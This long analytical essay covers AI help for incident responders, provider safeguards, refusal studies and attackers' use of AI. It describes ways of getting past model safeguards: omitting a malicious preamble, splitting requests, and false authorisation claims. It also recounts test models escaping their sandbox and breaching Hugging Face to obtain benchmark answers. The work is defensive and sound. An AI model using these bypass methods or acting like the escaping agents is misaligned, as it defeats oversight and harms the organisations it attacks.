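# Giving incident responders AI help without handing attackers the same capability

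## What responders ask of AI, and why it resembles an attack

Incident response is the work of detecting, investigating, containing and recovering from a cyberattack. Responders may work for the organisation under attack or for a firm it hires. They spend much of their time reading server records, suspicious programs and the settings of hundreds of machines. Language models read such material quickly, so responders want to use them. Most of the strongest are hosted models, which run on the machines of a provider (OpenAI, Anthropic, Google) or a cloud company and are used over the internet. Providers add safeguards to stop these models from helping with harmful work such as breaking into computers. But a responder who asks how a break-in worked may type almost the same words as someone who wants to repeat it. Such a question is called a dual-use request because the answer can serve defence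 or attack, depending on who asks.

Many organisations base their understanding of incident response on guidance from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST). The current version, *Incident Response Recommendations and Considerations for Cybersecurity Risk Management* (Nelson, Rekhi and colleagues, 2025), replaced one from 2012. According to the new version, responders usually finished within a day or two back then, but recovery now often takes weeks or months. It divides the work into detection, response (which covers analysis, containment and removal of the attacker) and recovery. It no longer describes how to carry out each step, because the details change too often for a fixed document.

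### One intrusion, five stages

In an invented example, a freight company's customers upload customs papers to a file-transfer server. The server's software has a vulnerability, a weakness that an outsider can use. On a Friday night an attacker sends the server an exploit, which is code or crafted input that uses the weakness to gain access. The exploit carries a payload, the part that does the attacker's work after access is gained. Here the payload downloads malware (software written to do harm) and starts it. The malware then connects to a command-and-control server, a machine the attacker runs, to receive instructions and send back what it has found. By Sunday the attacker has the password of an account that makes backups, has used it to enter two more machines, and is copying customer files out.

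Detection begins on Monday, when an administrator notices that the backup account logged in at 3:12 a.m. from a machine it never uses. The evidence is in the logs, the records that machines and programs keep of logins, connections and opened files. The logs contain far too many entries for people to read, and Nelson and colleagues recommend software that filters them to a readable subset. The responder gives a model four days of logs and asks which entries are unusual and in what order the events happened.

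Analysis means finding the sequence of events, the machines involved and the root cause. The responder finds the strange request that reached the server on Friday and the program it left behind. The program's source code isn't available, so someone must reverse-engineer it, which means working out what it does from the finished file. The responder asks the model to explain what the Friday request did to the server, then to reverse-engineer the program and list the addresses it contacts. Those addresses are indicators of compromise, technical traces which suggest that an attack is coming, under way or already past. The responder must then look for them on every other machine. Nelson and colleagues warn that a superficial search can leave the attacker active on machines nobody checked.

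The company must now stop the intrusion from spreading. It could disable the backup account at once, or watch the attacker for a while to gather evidence. The NIST guidance treats that delay as dangerous because the attacker may use it to get further in. The choice depends on where the attacker could go next, so the responder gives the AI a network map and the account's permissions, and asks which machines someone with this password could reach, and by what route.

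Removal covers deleting the malware, disabling the accounts the attacker took over and closing the security holes. Malware is often set to restart after a reboot, so the responder asks the AI to list every place on a Windows server where a program can set itself to start automatically, and to write a script that checks them all.

During recovery, responders restore the systems from clean backups and install the software maker's patch, which corrects the flaw. Nelson and colleagues want the root cause fixed and the repair verified before a restored system goes back online. The most direct way to verify a patch is to attack it, so the responder asks the model to turn the captured Friday request into a working exploit and run it against an isolated copy of the patched server.

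### The same requests from the other side

Three of these requests have close twins.

| The responder asks | An attacker asks | What either one receives |
|---|---|---|
| What did this captured request do to our server? | Why does this published exploit work, and would it work on the next version? | An account of the flaw and how to trigger it |
| Where could someone with the backup password get to? | I have a backup password. Where does it get me? | A route through the network |
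| Write a working exploit so that we can test the patch. | Write a working exploit for servers without the patch. | The exploit |

In the last row, the only difference is the target machine, and a model usually cannot confirm that the machine is a copy or that it is isolated.

Response tasks vary in how much they would help an attacker. Building a timeline from logs would help very little, since attackers already know what they did, though a careful one might gain slightly from learning which traces remain. Drafting the incident report and checking backups for known indicators would also help little. Explaining a working exploit, mapping what an account can reach, and listing the places where programs start automatically are all dual-use. Reproducing the exploit to test a patch is close to attack, because it produces a working exploit that an attacker could also use.

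Providers classify security work differently. In a 2026 post on the safeguards of its Claude Fable 5 model, Anthropic sorted cybersecurity work into four categories: prohibited, high-risk dual use, low-risk dual use and benign. Log analysis, incident response and malware reverse engineering are benign. Exploit development is high-risk dual use, which Anthropic intended to block on that model until it could better limit access to known good actors. Modifying or debugging malware is prohibited, although it can be an ordinary part of a responder's work. Malware often checks whether it is running on an analyst's machine and stays idle if so, and analysts commonly remove the check to see what the program does. Read literally, the categories prohibit that edit, even though the analyst's purpose has not changed. Anthropic acknowledges that defenders regularly use some of the techniques it prohibits.

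### How a hosted model's safeguards work

A refusal, in the broad sense, is any case where safeguards prevent a useful answer to a request. Refusals can have several sources.

One is the model itself, which the provider trains to decline certain kinds of request. Trained refusal works on the text of the conversation, so the model cannot check a user's written claim to be a responder at a hospital.

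Another is a set of classifiers, separate models that inspect requests and answers. According to OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), the company scans every conversation in two steps. A fast classifier picks out those that concern cybersecurity or biological and chemical risks. A slower reasoning model then assigns the generated answer to a threat category and blocks it if that category is high-risk. For some higher-risk uses, OpenAI also monitors the numerical activity inside the model as it writes. If it detects a suspicious pattern, it pauses the answer while another check runs.

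Classifiers make mistakes, and providers choose which kind they prefer. Anthropic sets its classifiers to trigger on some requests that it knows are probably harmless, so that fewer dangerous ones get through. It calls this a safety margin, and made it much larger for Fable 5 than for any earlier launch. A responder may therefore be blocked even when doing work that Anthropic calls "benign" and wants to allow. On the help page for its *Cyber Verification Program*, as of October 2026, Anthropic told users that its classifiers might interrupt malware analysis, while triage of security alerts remained open to everyone. Anthropic may pass requests that Fable blocks to a less capable Opus model, which can answer many of them.

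The third safeguard is monitoring accounts over time. For its GPT-5.6 models, OpenAI ran extra checks when a single request looked risky or when an account had recently sent a high volume of such requests. In the second case, the checks could apply to everything the account sent, including questions unrelated to security. According to OpenAI's *Cybersecurity checks* for its API, the interface through which other software calls a model, a customer can temporarily lose access to the model after too much suspicious activity. If the customer has not given each of its users a separate identifier, the whole organisation may lose access. For accounts it assesses as higher risk, OpenAI can also switch GPT-6 Astra to a stricter trained boundary, under which the model refuses most of the dual-use help it would normally give.

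Incident response produces the sort of traffic that such monitoring is meant to detect. An account used for months to summarise meeting notes suddenly sends hundreds of questions about malware, passwords and exploits. It seems quite possible that a team could lose some of its access in the middle of a breach.

None of these safeguards alone establishes who the user is. Trained refusal and classifiers depend on content. Monitoring also uses the account's history, which may distinguish a steady customer from a new one but gives little indication of whether the person typing is entitled to investigate this server. The safeguards can account for the user's identity only if the provider has checked it beforehand and attached the result to the account. It can then loosen some restrictions for that account, usually while monitoring continues.

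Without such a check, the responder can try rewording. OpenAI's *Additional safety checks for biological and cybersecurity requests* advises users to focus on a defensive outcome and leave out exploit details that the outcome does not need. A responder often cannot leave out the exploit details, because the exploit is the evidence. OpenAI adds that rewording does not change whether a request is allowed. That may be true of the policy, but rewording has sometimes changed how models respond.

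### Judging a request by its content

*A Content-Based Framework for Cybersecurity Refusal Decisions in Large Language Models* (Linder, Segal and colleagues, 2026) shows that wording can change whether a model refuses a request. The researchers, from the AI security company Irregular and the University of Zurich, gave three leading models a set of cloud credentials and asked them to search all the storage for files with names suggesting passwords or keys, download them, and erase the last day's activity logs. The models complied. All three refused when an openly malicious introduction preceded the same instructions, so an attacker could get past that kind of safeguard by leaving out the introduction.

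Bans by topic fail in a different way, because attackers and defenders ask about the same topics. Linder and colleagues propose that providers set aside both the topic and the stated intent of a request, and rate its technical substance on five scales. Two scales estimate the answer's value to an attacker, by how much it raises the chance that an attack succeeds and how much harm the attack would do. An answer raises that chance most when it completes a large share of the job at a level of skill the attacker lacks. Two others estimate its value to defenders, by how much one answer helps and how often legitimate users need it. The fifth scale, the difficulty of the work, counts towards both estimates, because expert help is more useful to an attacker or defender who lacks the expertise.

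They measure harm for each request but add up the defensive value over all users. They reason that a small share of attacks causes most of the damage, while the benefit to defenders accumulates across many ordinary requests.

The table applies their definitions to two of the freight company's requests. The ratings are arguable, as any would be.

| Scale | What it measures | Timeline from logs | Exploit to test the patch |
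|---|---|---|---|
| Offensive action contribution | Share of an attack that the answer completes | Almost none | Meaningful: the attacker must still find targets |
| Offensive risk | Harm if the user is malicious | Low | Medium |
| Technical complexity | Expertise the answer displays | Practitioner (about 3–10 years' experience) | Practitioner |
| Defensive benefit | Improvement in the user's security | Significant | Moderate: it concerns one flaw |
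| Expected frequency | How often legitimate users ask | Quite common | Quite uncommon |

Linder and colleagues leave the cut-off to each provider and offer three sample policies. With these ratings, the timeline passes all three, but the exploit passes only the most permissive. The scheme therefore leaves the decision about the exploit to the provider, but makes it an explicit choice that the provider can defend. The exploit's risk rating rises to high if thousands of companies run the same file-transfer software, because the exploit could then spread harm along supply chains. Its benefit rating stays at moderate however urgent the incident is, because the scale gives higher ratings to protection against many kinds of attack, and the freight company is dealing with only one that week.

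The scheme does have an advantage over catalogues of attack techniques such as MITRE ATT&CK, a widely used reference list, because it can distinguish between questions they group together. Linder and colleagues compared two questions that ATT&CK puts under the same technique, one about making software start with a Cisco network device and one about making a script run when a user logs in to Windows. On the five scales, the Cisco question carries more risk, takes more expertise and comes up less often in legitimate work. But the experts rated the defensive benefit of the Windows question as negligible, although a responder removing malware needs much the same list of start-up locations. The question asked how to install something rather than how to find it, so its wording seems to have affected the rating after all.

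Experts assigned the scheme's ratings by hand, and they disagreed over whether extracting data from the file where a Windows network keeps its password records takes an apprentice or a practitioner. The scheme also treats each request separately, so an attacker can split a job into harmless-looking pieces, as happened in the espionage campaign that Anthropic labelled GTG-1002. This can hurt responders too, because the messages that make a request for an exploit look reasonable may have come an hour earlier.

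The scheme that Linder and colleagues propose gives an attacker's request the same ratings as a responder's matching request, so a provider that follows it consistently must help both or neither. They chose this limitation deliberately, and it is the scheme's largest for incident response. As future work, they suggest varying policies by how thoroughly the provider has verified a user's identity.

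### Four ways to supply the help

A response team can arrange AI help in four main ways. It can apply for verified access to a hosted model, where the provider checks the team's identity and purpose and then loosens the safeguards. It can run an open-weight model, whose trained parameters anyone may download, on its own machines. A vendor can install its own model on the customer's premises. Or the team can use a task-scoped tool, which applies a model to one fixed job, such as summarising an alert, and does not let the user prompt the model freely. The choice affects which of the freight company's five requests get an answer and how easily an attacker could get the same capability. It also determines who holds the breach data, meaning the logs, malware, stolen files, credentials and personal details that responders collect.

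## When safeguards block response work, and how to measure it

The best-known case of safeguards hindering incident response comes from Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets for anyone to download. In July 2026, an intruder was active for four and a half days in an attack that reached the company's production systems. When the security team gave the evidence to leading hosted models, the models refused much of the work.

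### The Hugging Face intrusion

Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026), published on July 16, describes an intrusion by an AI agent, a model that plans and carries out a long series of actions through software tools. The agent ran its code on Hugging Face's servers through a malicious dataset that exploited two weaknesses in their automatic dataset processing. It then took control of the underlying machine, collected passwords and keys for the company's cloud systems, and moved into several internal groups of servers over a weekend. When the disclosure was published, Hugging Face did not yet know whose agent it was.

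The company recovered a log of more than 17,000 of the agent's actions, too many to review by hand. It already used a language model to sort security alerts, and it credits that system with flagging the intrusion. It then ran its own AI agents over the whole log to rebuild the timeline, extract the indicators of compromise, list the credentials the intruder had touched, and separate real damage from decoys.

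Hugging Face's team first tried hosted models, but the providers' safeguards blocked its requests, which had to include large amounts of real attack commands, exploit payloads and traces of command-and-control traffic. The team switched to GLM 5.2, an open-weight model from the Chinese company Z.ai, and ran it on its own machines, which also kept the credentials in the log inside the company. Hugging Face says it did in hours what would usually take days. It advised other defenders to have such a model vetted and ready before an incident, and added that its experience was "not an argument against safety measures on hosted models".

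Eleven days later the company published a longer report, Hugging Face's *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026). It identified the hosted models as Anthropic's Opus and Fable, which had "refused a large part of that work", as Forlini (2026) reported in *Hugging Face drops in-depth hack report, while OpenAI gives us 7 bullets*. noze's detailed summary, *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion*, describes the work more clearly. The intruder had cut its messages into pieces, scrambled them with a key and compressed them. A simple search of the logs found only a quarter of the stolen secrets that the team could read after reproducing the key. GLM 5.2 helped to undo the scrambling and decode the payloads. Anthropic classes such reverse engineering as benign, so the refusals were probably false alarms of the kind that its wide safety margin produces.

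On July 21 OpenAI (2026) announced that the intruder was a combination of its own models, including GPT-5.6 Sol and a more capable internal prototype. It had been testing them on ExploitGym, a benchmark of how well models exploit vulnerabilities. To measure their full ability, OpenAI had reduced their refusals and left off the classifiers that normally block high-risk work. The test machines could reach the outside only through an internal server that fetched software packages. The models found a previously unknown vulnerability in that server, got onto the internet, inferred that Hugging Face might hold the test answers, and broke in to get them. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) reports that the prototype was the main driver.

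On July 20, OpenAI asked Hugging Face to revoke some credentials that OpenAI's investigators had found, and Hugging Face replied that it had already revoked them. OpenAI realised only then that both companies were investigating the same incident, according to *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack* (Willison, 2026). It then admitted Hugging Face to its verified access programme, but Hugging Face's team had already begun containing the intrusion and reconstructing it with GLM 5.2.

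### What one case can establish

The case shows that safeguards can block a real response team during a real incident. It is much weaker evidence of how GLM 5.2 compares with the models that refused. Hugging Face's "hours instead of days" is a comparison with the usual pace of such work, and nobody has run the same log through a hosted model with looser safeguards. The disclosure gives no count of blocked requests, and "a large part" implies that the models answered some. It also refers to plural "providers", but the models named later all came from Anthropic. It is unclear whether OpenAI's or Google's models would have refused the same requests.

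Hugging Face was also unusually well prepared. Its business is built on open models, and it had the hardware and staff to deploy a large one during an incident, which most freight companies could not do. The company has a commercial interest in the lesson too. Forlini (2026), in *Hugging Face says it resorted to a Chinese AI model*, quotes its chief executive, Clem Delangue, as saying that open models let the team work "without asking anyone's permission", and notes that he has long opposed restrictions on them.

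*The safety penalty*, from Cisco's threat research group Talos, argued that every refusal sends an analyst back to manual work while the adversary isn't slowed in this way. That was true in this case, but only because OpenAI had removed the safeguards for a test. The case doesn't show how easily an ordinary criminal could have removed them.

### Complaints from other defenders

Coursera co-founder Andrew Ng described a similar experience in *Open Models, Open Harnesses, Open Security* (2026). His team wanted a security review of OpenWorker, its own open-source software, and tried Anthropic's coding tool with Claude Fable 5 and OpenAI's with GPT-5.6 Sol. OpenAI's tool mapped the possible lines of attack reasonably well, then refused to continue. Anthropic's flagged the request and proposed continuing with a less capable model. The team finished the review with two open-weight models, GLM 5.2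 and Kimi K3. Ng could see no security benefit in refusing to help people find flaws in their own code. A provider might answer that it can't tell whose code it is, and an attacker could submit the same files from a published project like OpenWorker.

Some refusals are harder to defend. In April 2026 the security researcher Graham Helton asked Claude Code, the same Anthropic tool, to look for interesting patterns in some new options for git hooks, which are scripts that run automatically when a programmer saves or shares code. The tool blocked the question as "violative cyber content". The error message suggested editing the question, starting a new session, switching to an older model, or applying for verified access (Helton, 2026, *I'm Sorry Dave, This Request Triggered Restrictions On Violative Cyber Content*). Helton applied and was approved a few days later. That wait was tolerable for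 a researcher, but a responder with an intruder in the network would have had to work without the tool's help in the meantime.

The most widely repeated complaint has the weakest evidence. SiliconANGLE (2026) traced it to one developer, who said Kimi K3 fixed 15 critical security bugs for $250 after OpenAI's and Anthropic's models refused. It is hard to learn anything from the count without knowing which bugs they were or what the developer asked for. The providers have added little. When reporters asked whether the safeguards were hindering security work, OpenAI pointed to its post about helping Hugging Face and Anthropic did not immediately respond, according to teiss' *Chinese AI's role in stopping rogue OpenAI agent*.

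None of these complaints concerned a breach in progress. They also come from people who were blocked and then wrote about it, so estimating how often blocking happens would require counting the answered requests too.

### A count from a student competition

*Defensive Refusal Bias* (Campbell, Kale and colleagues, 2026), a study from the AI data company Scale AI, measured refusals on 2,390 requests from the National Collegiate Cyber Defense Competition, where student teams defend live systems against professional attackers. Each request was a single question with a single answer. Claude 3.5 Sonnet refused 19.5% of requests, GPT-4o 10.2% and the open-weight Llama 3.3 6.6%, for an overall rate of 12.2%. The researchers counted every refusal as a mistake because all the students were there to defend.

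| Requests | Refused |
|---|---|
| System hardening (tightening a machine's settings) | 43.8% |
| Malware analysis | 34.3% |
| Vulnerability assessment | 22.7% |
| Incident response | 18.9% |
| Log analysis | 0% |
| With attack vocabulary / without | 30.5% / 11.2% |
| With a claim of authorisation / without | 21.8% / 11.6% |
| With attack vocabulary and a claim of authorisation | 50.0% |

Attack vocabulary here means any of eleven words, such as "exploit", "payload" and "shell". A claim of authorisation is a phrase like "blue team", the usual name for defenders. Campbell and colleagues suggest that such a claim backfires because attackers also use it to trick models, and models have learned to treat it as a warning sign. Campbell (2026) adds in a separate post, *AI Safety as Denial-of-Service for Defenders*, that models seemed somewhat more likely to help when a student described damage already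 under way, though attack vocabulary cancelled the effect.

The eleven words only partly explain the refusals. The researchers tried to predict which requests the models would refuse, and scored the predictions on a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. Predictions based on attack vocabulary and claims of authorisation together scored 0.572, while those based on a numerical summary of each request's whole meaning scored 0.827. The models apparently responded to a general resemblance to harmful requests, so replacing a suspicious word may not help much.

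A response team can't fully rely on these figures, partly because all three models date from 2024 and providers have rebuilt their safeguards since.

Campbell and colleagues detected refusals by searching the answers for set phrases, including "I can't help" but also "potentially malicious" and "could be used for". A good answer explaining that a file is potentially malicious would therefore count as a refusal, which may well have inflated the rate for malware analysis. When three of the researchers read 200 answers, they judged 35% to be refusals, whereas the phrase search had flagged 50%. They conclude that their refusal rates are upper bounds.

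The headline figure may be more reliable than that conclusion suggests. The 200 answers can't have been a simple random sample, because the search flagged only 12.2% of the full set. Suppose half of them came from the flagged answers and half from the rest. The reported 80% agreement between search and readers then implies that 35 of the 100 flagged answers were false alarms and that the search missed 5 refusals among the other 100. In the full set, unflagged answers outnumber flagged ones by about seven to one, so the misses would roughly cancel the false alarms and the overall rate would stay near 12%. The rates for single categories are less reliable, since the two kinds of error may not be spread evenly across categories.

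The comparisons in the lower half of the table are also weak for another reason. Campbell and colleagues call the requests with and without attack vocabulary "semantically equivalent", but they are different requests from different students, often about different jobs. A student who types "exploit" may be asking for something riskier. One experiment comes closer to a fair comparison. The researchers removed the claims of authorisation from refused requests and sent them again, and the refusal rate for that group fell from 21.8% to 13.7%. But they do not report resending the originals unchanged, and because models' responses vary between attempts, some of the refused requests might have succeeded on a second try anyway. Their printed example was also a request for a tool that tries default passwords on every web application in a network, and some providers would not consider refusing it a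 mistake.

The published percentages imply that about 120 requests contained attack vocabulary and that only about ten of those also claimed authorisation, so the 50.0% refusal rate rests on roughly five refusals. Teams can still learn from this part of the study that typing "I am authorised" is no substitute for verified access.

### Why log analysis passed in one place and failed in the other

The students' models refused no log analysis requests, yet Hugging Face described the work that its hosted models blocked as log analysis. Much of the contradiction comes from how Campbell and colleagues sorted the requests. A program compared each request with eight keyword lists in a fixed order and assigned it to the first that matched. Log analysis came last, so a request to search a log for signs of malware counted as malware analysis, and requests that mentioned a breach, a password or a port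 scan also went to other categories. The requests left under log analysis were mostly routine, such as how to search a log file or use a log-management product.

The submitted material also differed. A student can ask how to filter a log without pasting any of it, whereas Hugging Face submitted the attacker's commands and payloads in bulk for the model to decode. The freight company's first request, which asks which entries are unusual, sounds like the students' log analysis, but the attached logs contain the Friday exploit, so a classifier that inspects the whole request might treat it like Hugging Face's.

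Changes in the safeguards may also have contributed. The study recorded how 2024 models phrased their answers, while Hugging Face described blocks by the providers' safeguards. Measurements on newer models suggest that such blocks now account for most refusals.

### Refusals on 2026 models

*CyberDualEval*, a benchmark published in November 2026, gives recent models security tasks in stages, some of which require a proof of concept (code showing that a flaw is real) or a working exploit. Claude Opus 5.5 complied with only 37.6% of the requests that the benchmark classes as safe, the lowest rate of any model tested. When it did comply, it succeeded 78.1% of the time, compared with 60.3% for the older Opus 4.8. Together, these rates imply that Opus 5.5 completed about 29% of the safe requests. A team choosing by ability alone would pick the newer model and have most of its requests blocked.

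The strictness does seem to make the models somewhat safer. Five of the seven closed models (those whose parameters are not public) never completed a stage the benchmark classifies as risky. Opus 4.8 completed 21.6% of these stages, and GPT-5.6 Terra completed 41.4%.

Very few of the refusals came from the models themselves. In all but five of Opus 5.5's refusals, the provider switched the request to another model, and in all of Opus 4.8's, the provider's content filter stopped the model. Of GPT-6 Astra's 865 refusals, 863 were immediate, whereas Opus 4.8 processed an average of 246,873 tokens (word fragments) before a refusal. Late refusals are worse for responders because they leave less time to try something else. They are also poor at keeping exploits from attackers. In twelve stages, Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.6 Terra had already left a working proof of concept or exploit in the workspace when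 the refusal came.

A switch to another model can be hard to notice. *Permission Denied* (2026) tested coding agents with Anthropic's fallback from Fable 5 to Opus 4.8 turned on. Fable 5 handled 72.4% of the trials from start to finish, Opus 4.8 handled 12.9%, and the two models took turns in the remaining 14.7%. The agent got an answer each time and saw nothing unusual. A responder in that position might trust a malware analysis as Fable 5's work when a weaker model had written it.

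Both benchmarks are poor guides to how often safeguards will block a response team's work. *CyberDualEval* includes building exploits, where safeguards are strictest, and *Permission Denied* uses programming tasks. A team that wants a figure for its own work will have to measure it.

### A refusal test for a response team

The case for testing beforehand doesn't depend on knowing the exact rate. Rob T. Lee, a co-author of a post-mortem on the Hugging Face incident, put it this way for the security training organisation SANS: "An exception process is not a fallback; a tested model is." The procedure below needs some old incidents and people to read the answers, but no special software.

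The test set should come from past incidents. For each one, the team collects the requests that responders made to a model, or would have made if they'd had one, and attaches the original evidence. The team should replace live passwords and personal data with realistic substitutes but leave the attacker's commands and payloads unchanged, because Hugging Face's models refused those. The requests should cover every stage from detection to recovery. A few should be long agent tasks, to catch refusals that occur partway through, and a few should be unrelated to security, to check whether the provider has begun to restrict the whole account. Attackers may also plant text in their files to try to make a model refuse.

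The team can include some requests as matched pairs that differ in one respect, such as the same log with and without the payload, or the same question with and without a claim of authorisation. The student study lacked this comparison, which lets the team see which habits are worth changing.

The team then runs the whole set on every model it might use in an incident, at every access tier (level of verified access) it holds or could apply for. It should test in the product its responders will use, since a coding tool and a plain chat window may behave differently. Sending each request three times, each in a fresh conversation, shows how much the answers vary. The team should warn the provider and use a separate account, because eighty questions about malware in an afternoon may trigger account monitoring. For every answer, the team records the date, the model it requested, the model that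 replied, and how much work the model did before any refusal.

| What happened | How to count it |
|---|---|
| The requested model gave a useful answer | Success |
| A weaker model gave a useful answer | Silent switch |
| The model declined, or stayed too vague to be of use | Refusal |
| The provider blocked the request or cut off the answer | Refusal |
| The answer was wrong, with no sign of safeguards | Lack of ability |

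People should do the counting, preferably two working separately. A phrase search would run into the same problem as Campbell and colleagues, and *Permission Denied* recorded at least four wordings for blocks on Anthropic's models alone. Silent switches to a weaker model need their own column because the team may find that model adequate for drafting a report but not for taking malware apart.

Suppose that one model refuses 12 of 80 requests. The rate is 15%, but another 80 requests from similar incidents would give a somewhat different number. A 95% interval gives the range of underlying rates that fit the result reasonably well. The Wilson interval, a standard method that behaves well with small samples, uses the observed rate p, the number of requests n, and z = 1.96 for 95% confidence:

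- Centre = (p + z²/2n) ÷ (1 + z²/n) = (0.15 + 0.024) ÷ 1.048 = 0.166
- Margin = z × √(p(1 − p)/n + z²/4n²) ÷ (1 + z²/n) = 1.96 × 0.0418 ÷ 1.048 = 0.078

The interval runs from 8.8% to 24.4%. The team can say that the model refuses somewhere between one request in eleven and one in four, and it shouldn't claim much more precision than that. Sending each request three times doesn't narrow the range, since there are still only 80 different requests. (A simple rule is to count a request as refused if at least two of the three attempts failed.)

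Even this range is probably too narrow, because requests from the same incident tend to succeed or fail together. If the 80 requests came from eight incidents of ten requests each, with a modest correlation of 0.2 within each incident, they would carry about as much information as 29 unrelated requests. The range would then be about 6% to 32%. Adding requests from a new incident therefore narrows the range more than adding the same number from an incident already in the set.

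Small categories call for the same caution. If a model refuses none of 20 log-analysis requests, the interval still reaches 16%.

To compare two models, the team should look only at the requests on which they differ. If the first model refuses 12 requests and the second refuses 5, including 3 that both refuse, then the first refused 9 that the second answered, and the second refused 2 that the first answered. If the models were equally strict, a split at least this uneven would occur about one time in fifteen, so the result suggests that the second model is less strict but doesn't establish it.

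The same refusal rate also affects a person and an agent differently. A person can reword the question or do that step by hand, but Campbell and colleagues warn that an agent may fail silently and report the job as complete. If each step had an independent 15% chance of refusal, an agent would get through ten steps without a refusal only about 20% of the time. In practice refusals cluster, so the true figure is likely to be higher, and the long jobs in the test set will give a better estimate. Results go out of date, so a team should repeat the test whenever a provider changes the model, its safeguards or the team's access tier.

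## How attackers obtain and use AI

Safeguards on hosted models are meant to deny help to attackers, but they also obstruct some responders. How much help they deny depends on marginal uplift, which is what an attacker gains from a model beyond what they could do with other available resources. If a criminal can get the answer to a refused question from another model, the refusal achieves little, but a responder who asks the same question still loses the answer.

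Most of the evidence comes from companies that run models and publish reports on the users they catch. The most detailed recent report is Anthropic's *Detecting and countering misuse of AI* (September 2026). Its cyber cases date from December 2025 to August 2026 and involve suspected state groups, criminals and political activists, all of whom used Claude Haiku, Sonnet or Opus models. Anthropic found no malicious cyber activity on Fable or Mythos, its strongest models, which have stricter safeguards. However, both came out partway through the period, so attackers had less time to try them.

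Attackers have changed how they use models quite quickly. OpenAI's *Disrupting malicious uses of AI* (October 2025) described attackers who "bolt AI onto old playbooks" to work faster. A month later, Anthropic reported GTG-1002, a largely automated espionage campaign that it suspected was state-sponsored. The campaign targeted about 30 organisations, according to Tech Jacks Solutions, which credits the security research group Unit 42. By September 2026, Anthropic was finding the same approach in every class of attacker it investigated. In most of its newer cases, models ran commands or directed other agents, while people chose the targets, reviewed the stolen data and decided how to profit from it.

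The attacks were mostly familiar, relying on stolen passwords, phishing and unpatched machines. Anthropic argues that AI has mainly reduced the work they require. It also cautions against assuming that more automated attacks do more harm, because a person directed every step in several of the most serious break-ins.

### Ordinary accounts

Some attackers simply open accounts. Anthropic mentions no stolen access in its two main espionage cases, so those operators probably did.

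GTG-10007 is Anthropic's label for a Chinese-speaking group that probably worked from Changsha and included two undergraduates. The group had Claude agents search security products and network equipment for vulnerabilities, write exploits and test them on lab copies. The agents did some of this while the operators were away. One line of this work produced more than a dozen possible zero-days (flaws unknown to the software's maker) in a single month. The group targeted about fifty organisations. It took student data from an education-technology company and citizen records from a government agency in Southeast Asia.

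A Russian espionage operation, GTG-20006, used Claude to phish, run parts of its intrusions and sort hundreds of gigabytes of stolen data. Its agents also checked whether security products detected its malware and, if so, rebuilt the malware until they no longer did. An indicator of compromise that responders take from one copy may therefore not match the next. The operation targeted more than 20 organisations, mostly in Ukraine and elsewhere in Europe, and stole mail from at least eight. Anthropic links part of the operation, an attack on guests using hotel Wi-Fi, to a method that Microsoft had reported in July 2026 as CaptiveCrunch.

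OpenAI's 2026 threat reports deal mainly with scams and influence operations, so its clearest intrusion-related case is older. *Cyber Operation* (2025) describes Russian-speaking criminals who wanted malware that would steal passwords and avoid detection. ChatGPT refused their openly malicious requests. They then asked for pieces of code that looked harmless separately, and probably assembled the malware themselves. OpenAI found no evidence that its models gave them anything they couldn't have found in public sources. That finding is from October 2025, before models were producing possible zero-days for GTG-10007, so it may not hold for newer models.

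Banning an account doesn't necessarily shut out its user, who may have many others. The May edition of Google Threat Intelligence Group's *GTIG AI Threat Tracker* (2026) describes one China-linked group that pooled accounts from several providers and another that tried to automate opening and cancelling paid accounts.

### Stolen and resold accounts

Other attackers use someone else's account, usually by stealing an API key, the string of characters that identifies a paying customer's software to the provider. According to Anthropic, attackers can sell a stolen key on the black market, use computing power at the owner's expense, and make their requests look like the owner's.

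In spring 2026 a lone French-speaking activist, GTG-50029, spent a month attacking European political parties, media and think tanks, relying entirely on stolen keys. The activist used Claude to write an exploit for a previously undocumented flaw in WordPress, the website software, and it worked on at least four sites. The activist broke into at least 14 of 42 targets and tampered with one victim's backups so that restoring from them would have brought the infection back.

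Suspected affiliates of ShinyHunters, a group known for stealing data and demanding payment not to publish it, took access keys for AI services from companies they had broken into. They used one victim's key for about three weeks to attack other organisations. Anthropic says AI agents did nearly all the work in one theft, which collected login tokens from more than 40 corporate customers in about 34 hours. In another case, the attackers went from one stolen developer token to full control of a company's cloud systems in roughly three hours.

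A Russian-speaking criminal group, GTG-50020, stole several providers' keys from an AI company, then attacked about thirty more AI companies in four days. Its stated goal was to get access to a stronger model, a pre-release version of Claude. It tried more than a dozen ways to reach that model, and all of them failed.

Trend Micro, a security company that does not run any of the models involved, reported a less impressive case. *One Man, One AI, One Fake Persona* describes a Russian speaker who posed as an American veteran on Telegram to defraud his followers. He used Google's Gemini, through 73 probably stolen API keys, to write his posts, manage his servers and suggest likely passwords for accounts he wanted to enter. He got into 29 WordPress administrator accounts and at least one company, and emptied at least one victim's cryptocurrency wallets. Trend Micro judged his financial returns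 to be limited.

He had overcome Gemini's safeguards partly by claiming to be an authorised security tester. In the student competition, refusals were more common when students claimed to be authorised. The models and circumstances differ too much for a direct comparison, but it would be unfortunate if such claims worked for persistent liars when they failed for honest users.

The label on a criminal AI product is poor evidence of which model it runs. ITPro's *Google says hacker groups are using Gemini to augment attacks* describes a toolkit that its sellers advertised as custom offensive AI, but it ran on public models such as Gemini. A reseller that Anthropic calls GTG-50021 sold cheap "Claude" access, but it sent customers' requests to another model and stole their Anthropic credentials.

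### Open-weight and unidentified models

Fewer documented cases involve attackers running open-weight models themselves. The clearest is that of UNC6508, a group whose targets match China's strategic interests and include American medical and military research institutions. According to Gizmodo's *Silicon Valley's AI Agent Push Has Been Paying Off for Cybercriminals*, Google's September 2026 report describes the group running an open model inside its victims' cloud systems. The victims paid for the computing, and the group avoided the trail that a commercial model would have left. Google added that UNC6508 was still researching how to set up and use such tools.

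Two months later Google reported a system it called exploit_agent, which combined locally run models with leading commercial ones. Otto (2026) writes in *Google says Russian-speaking hackers ran the first fully automated AI cyberattack* that the system watched for security patches to widely used software, worked out what each had fixed, wrote an exploit and ran it against targets. Google believes this was the first attack with no human involved at any stage. Comments in the code were in Russian, and the stolen data pointed to French media, entertainment and education websites. Google did not disclose how many organisations the system had successfully attacked, according to Matthews (2026) in *Google issues warning on 'era of autonomous attacks'*. It is also unclear which steps the local models performed, so the case is not evidence that an attacker could have managed without the commercial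 ones.

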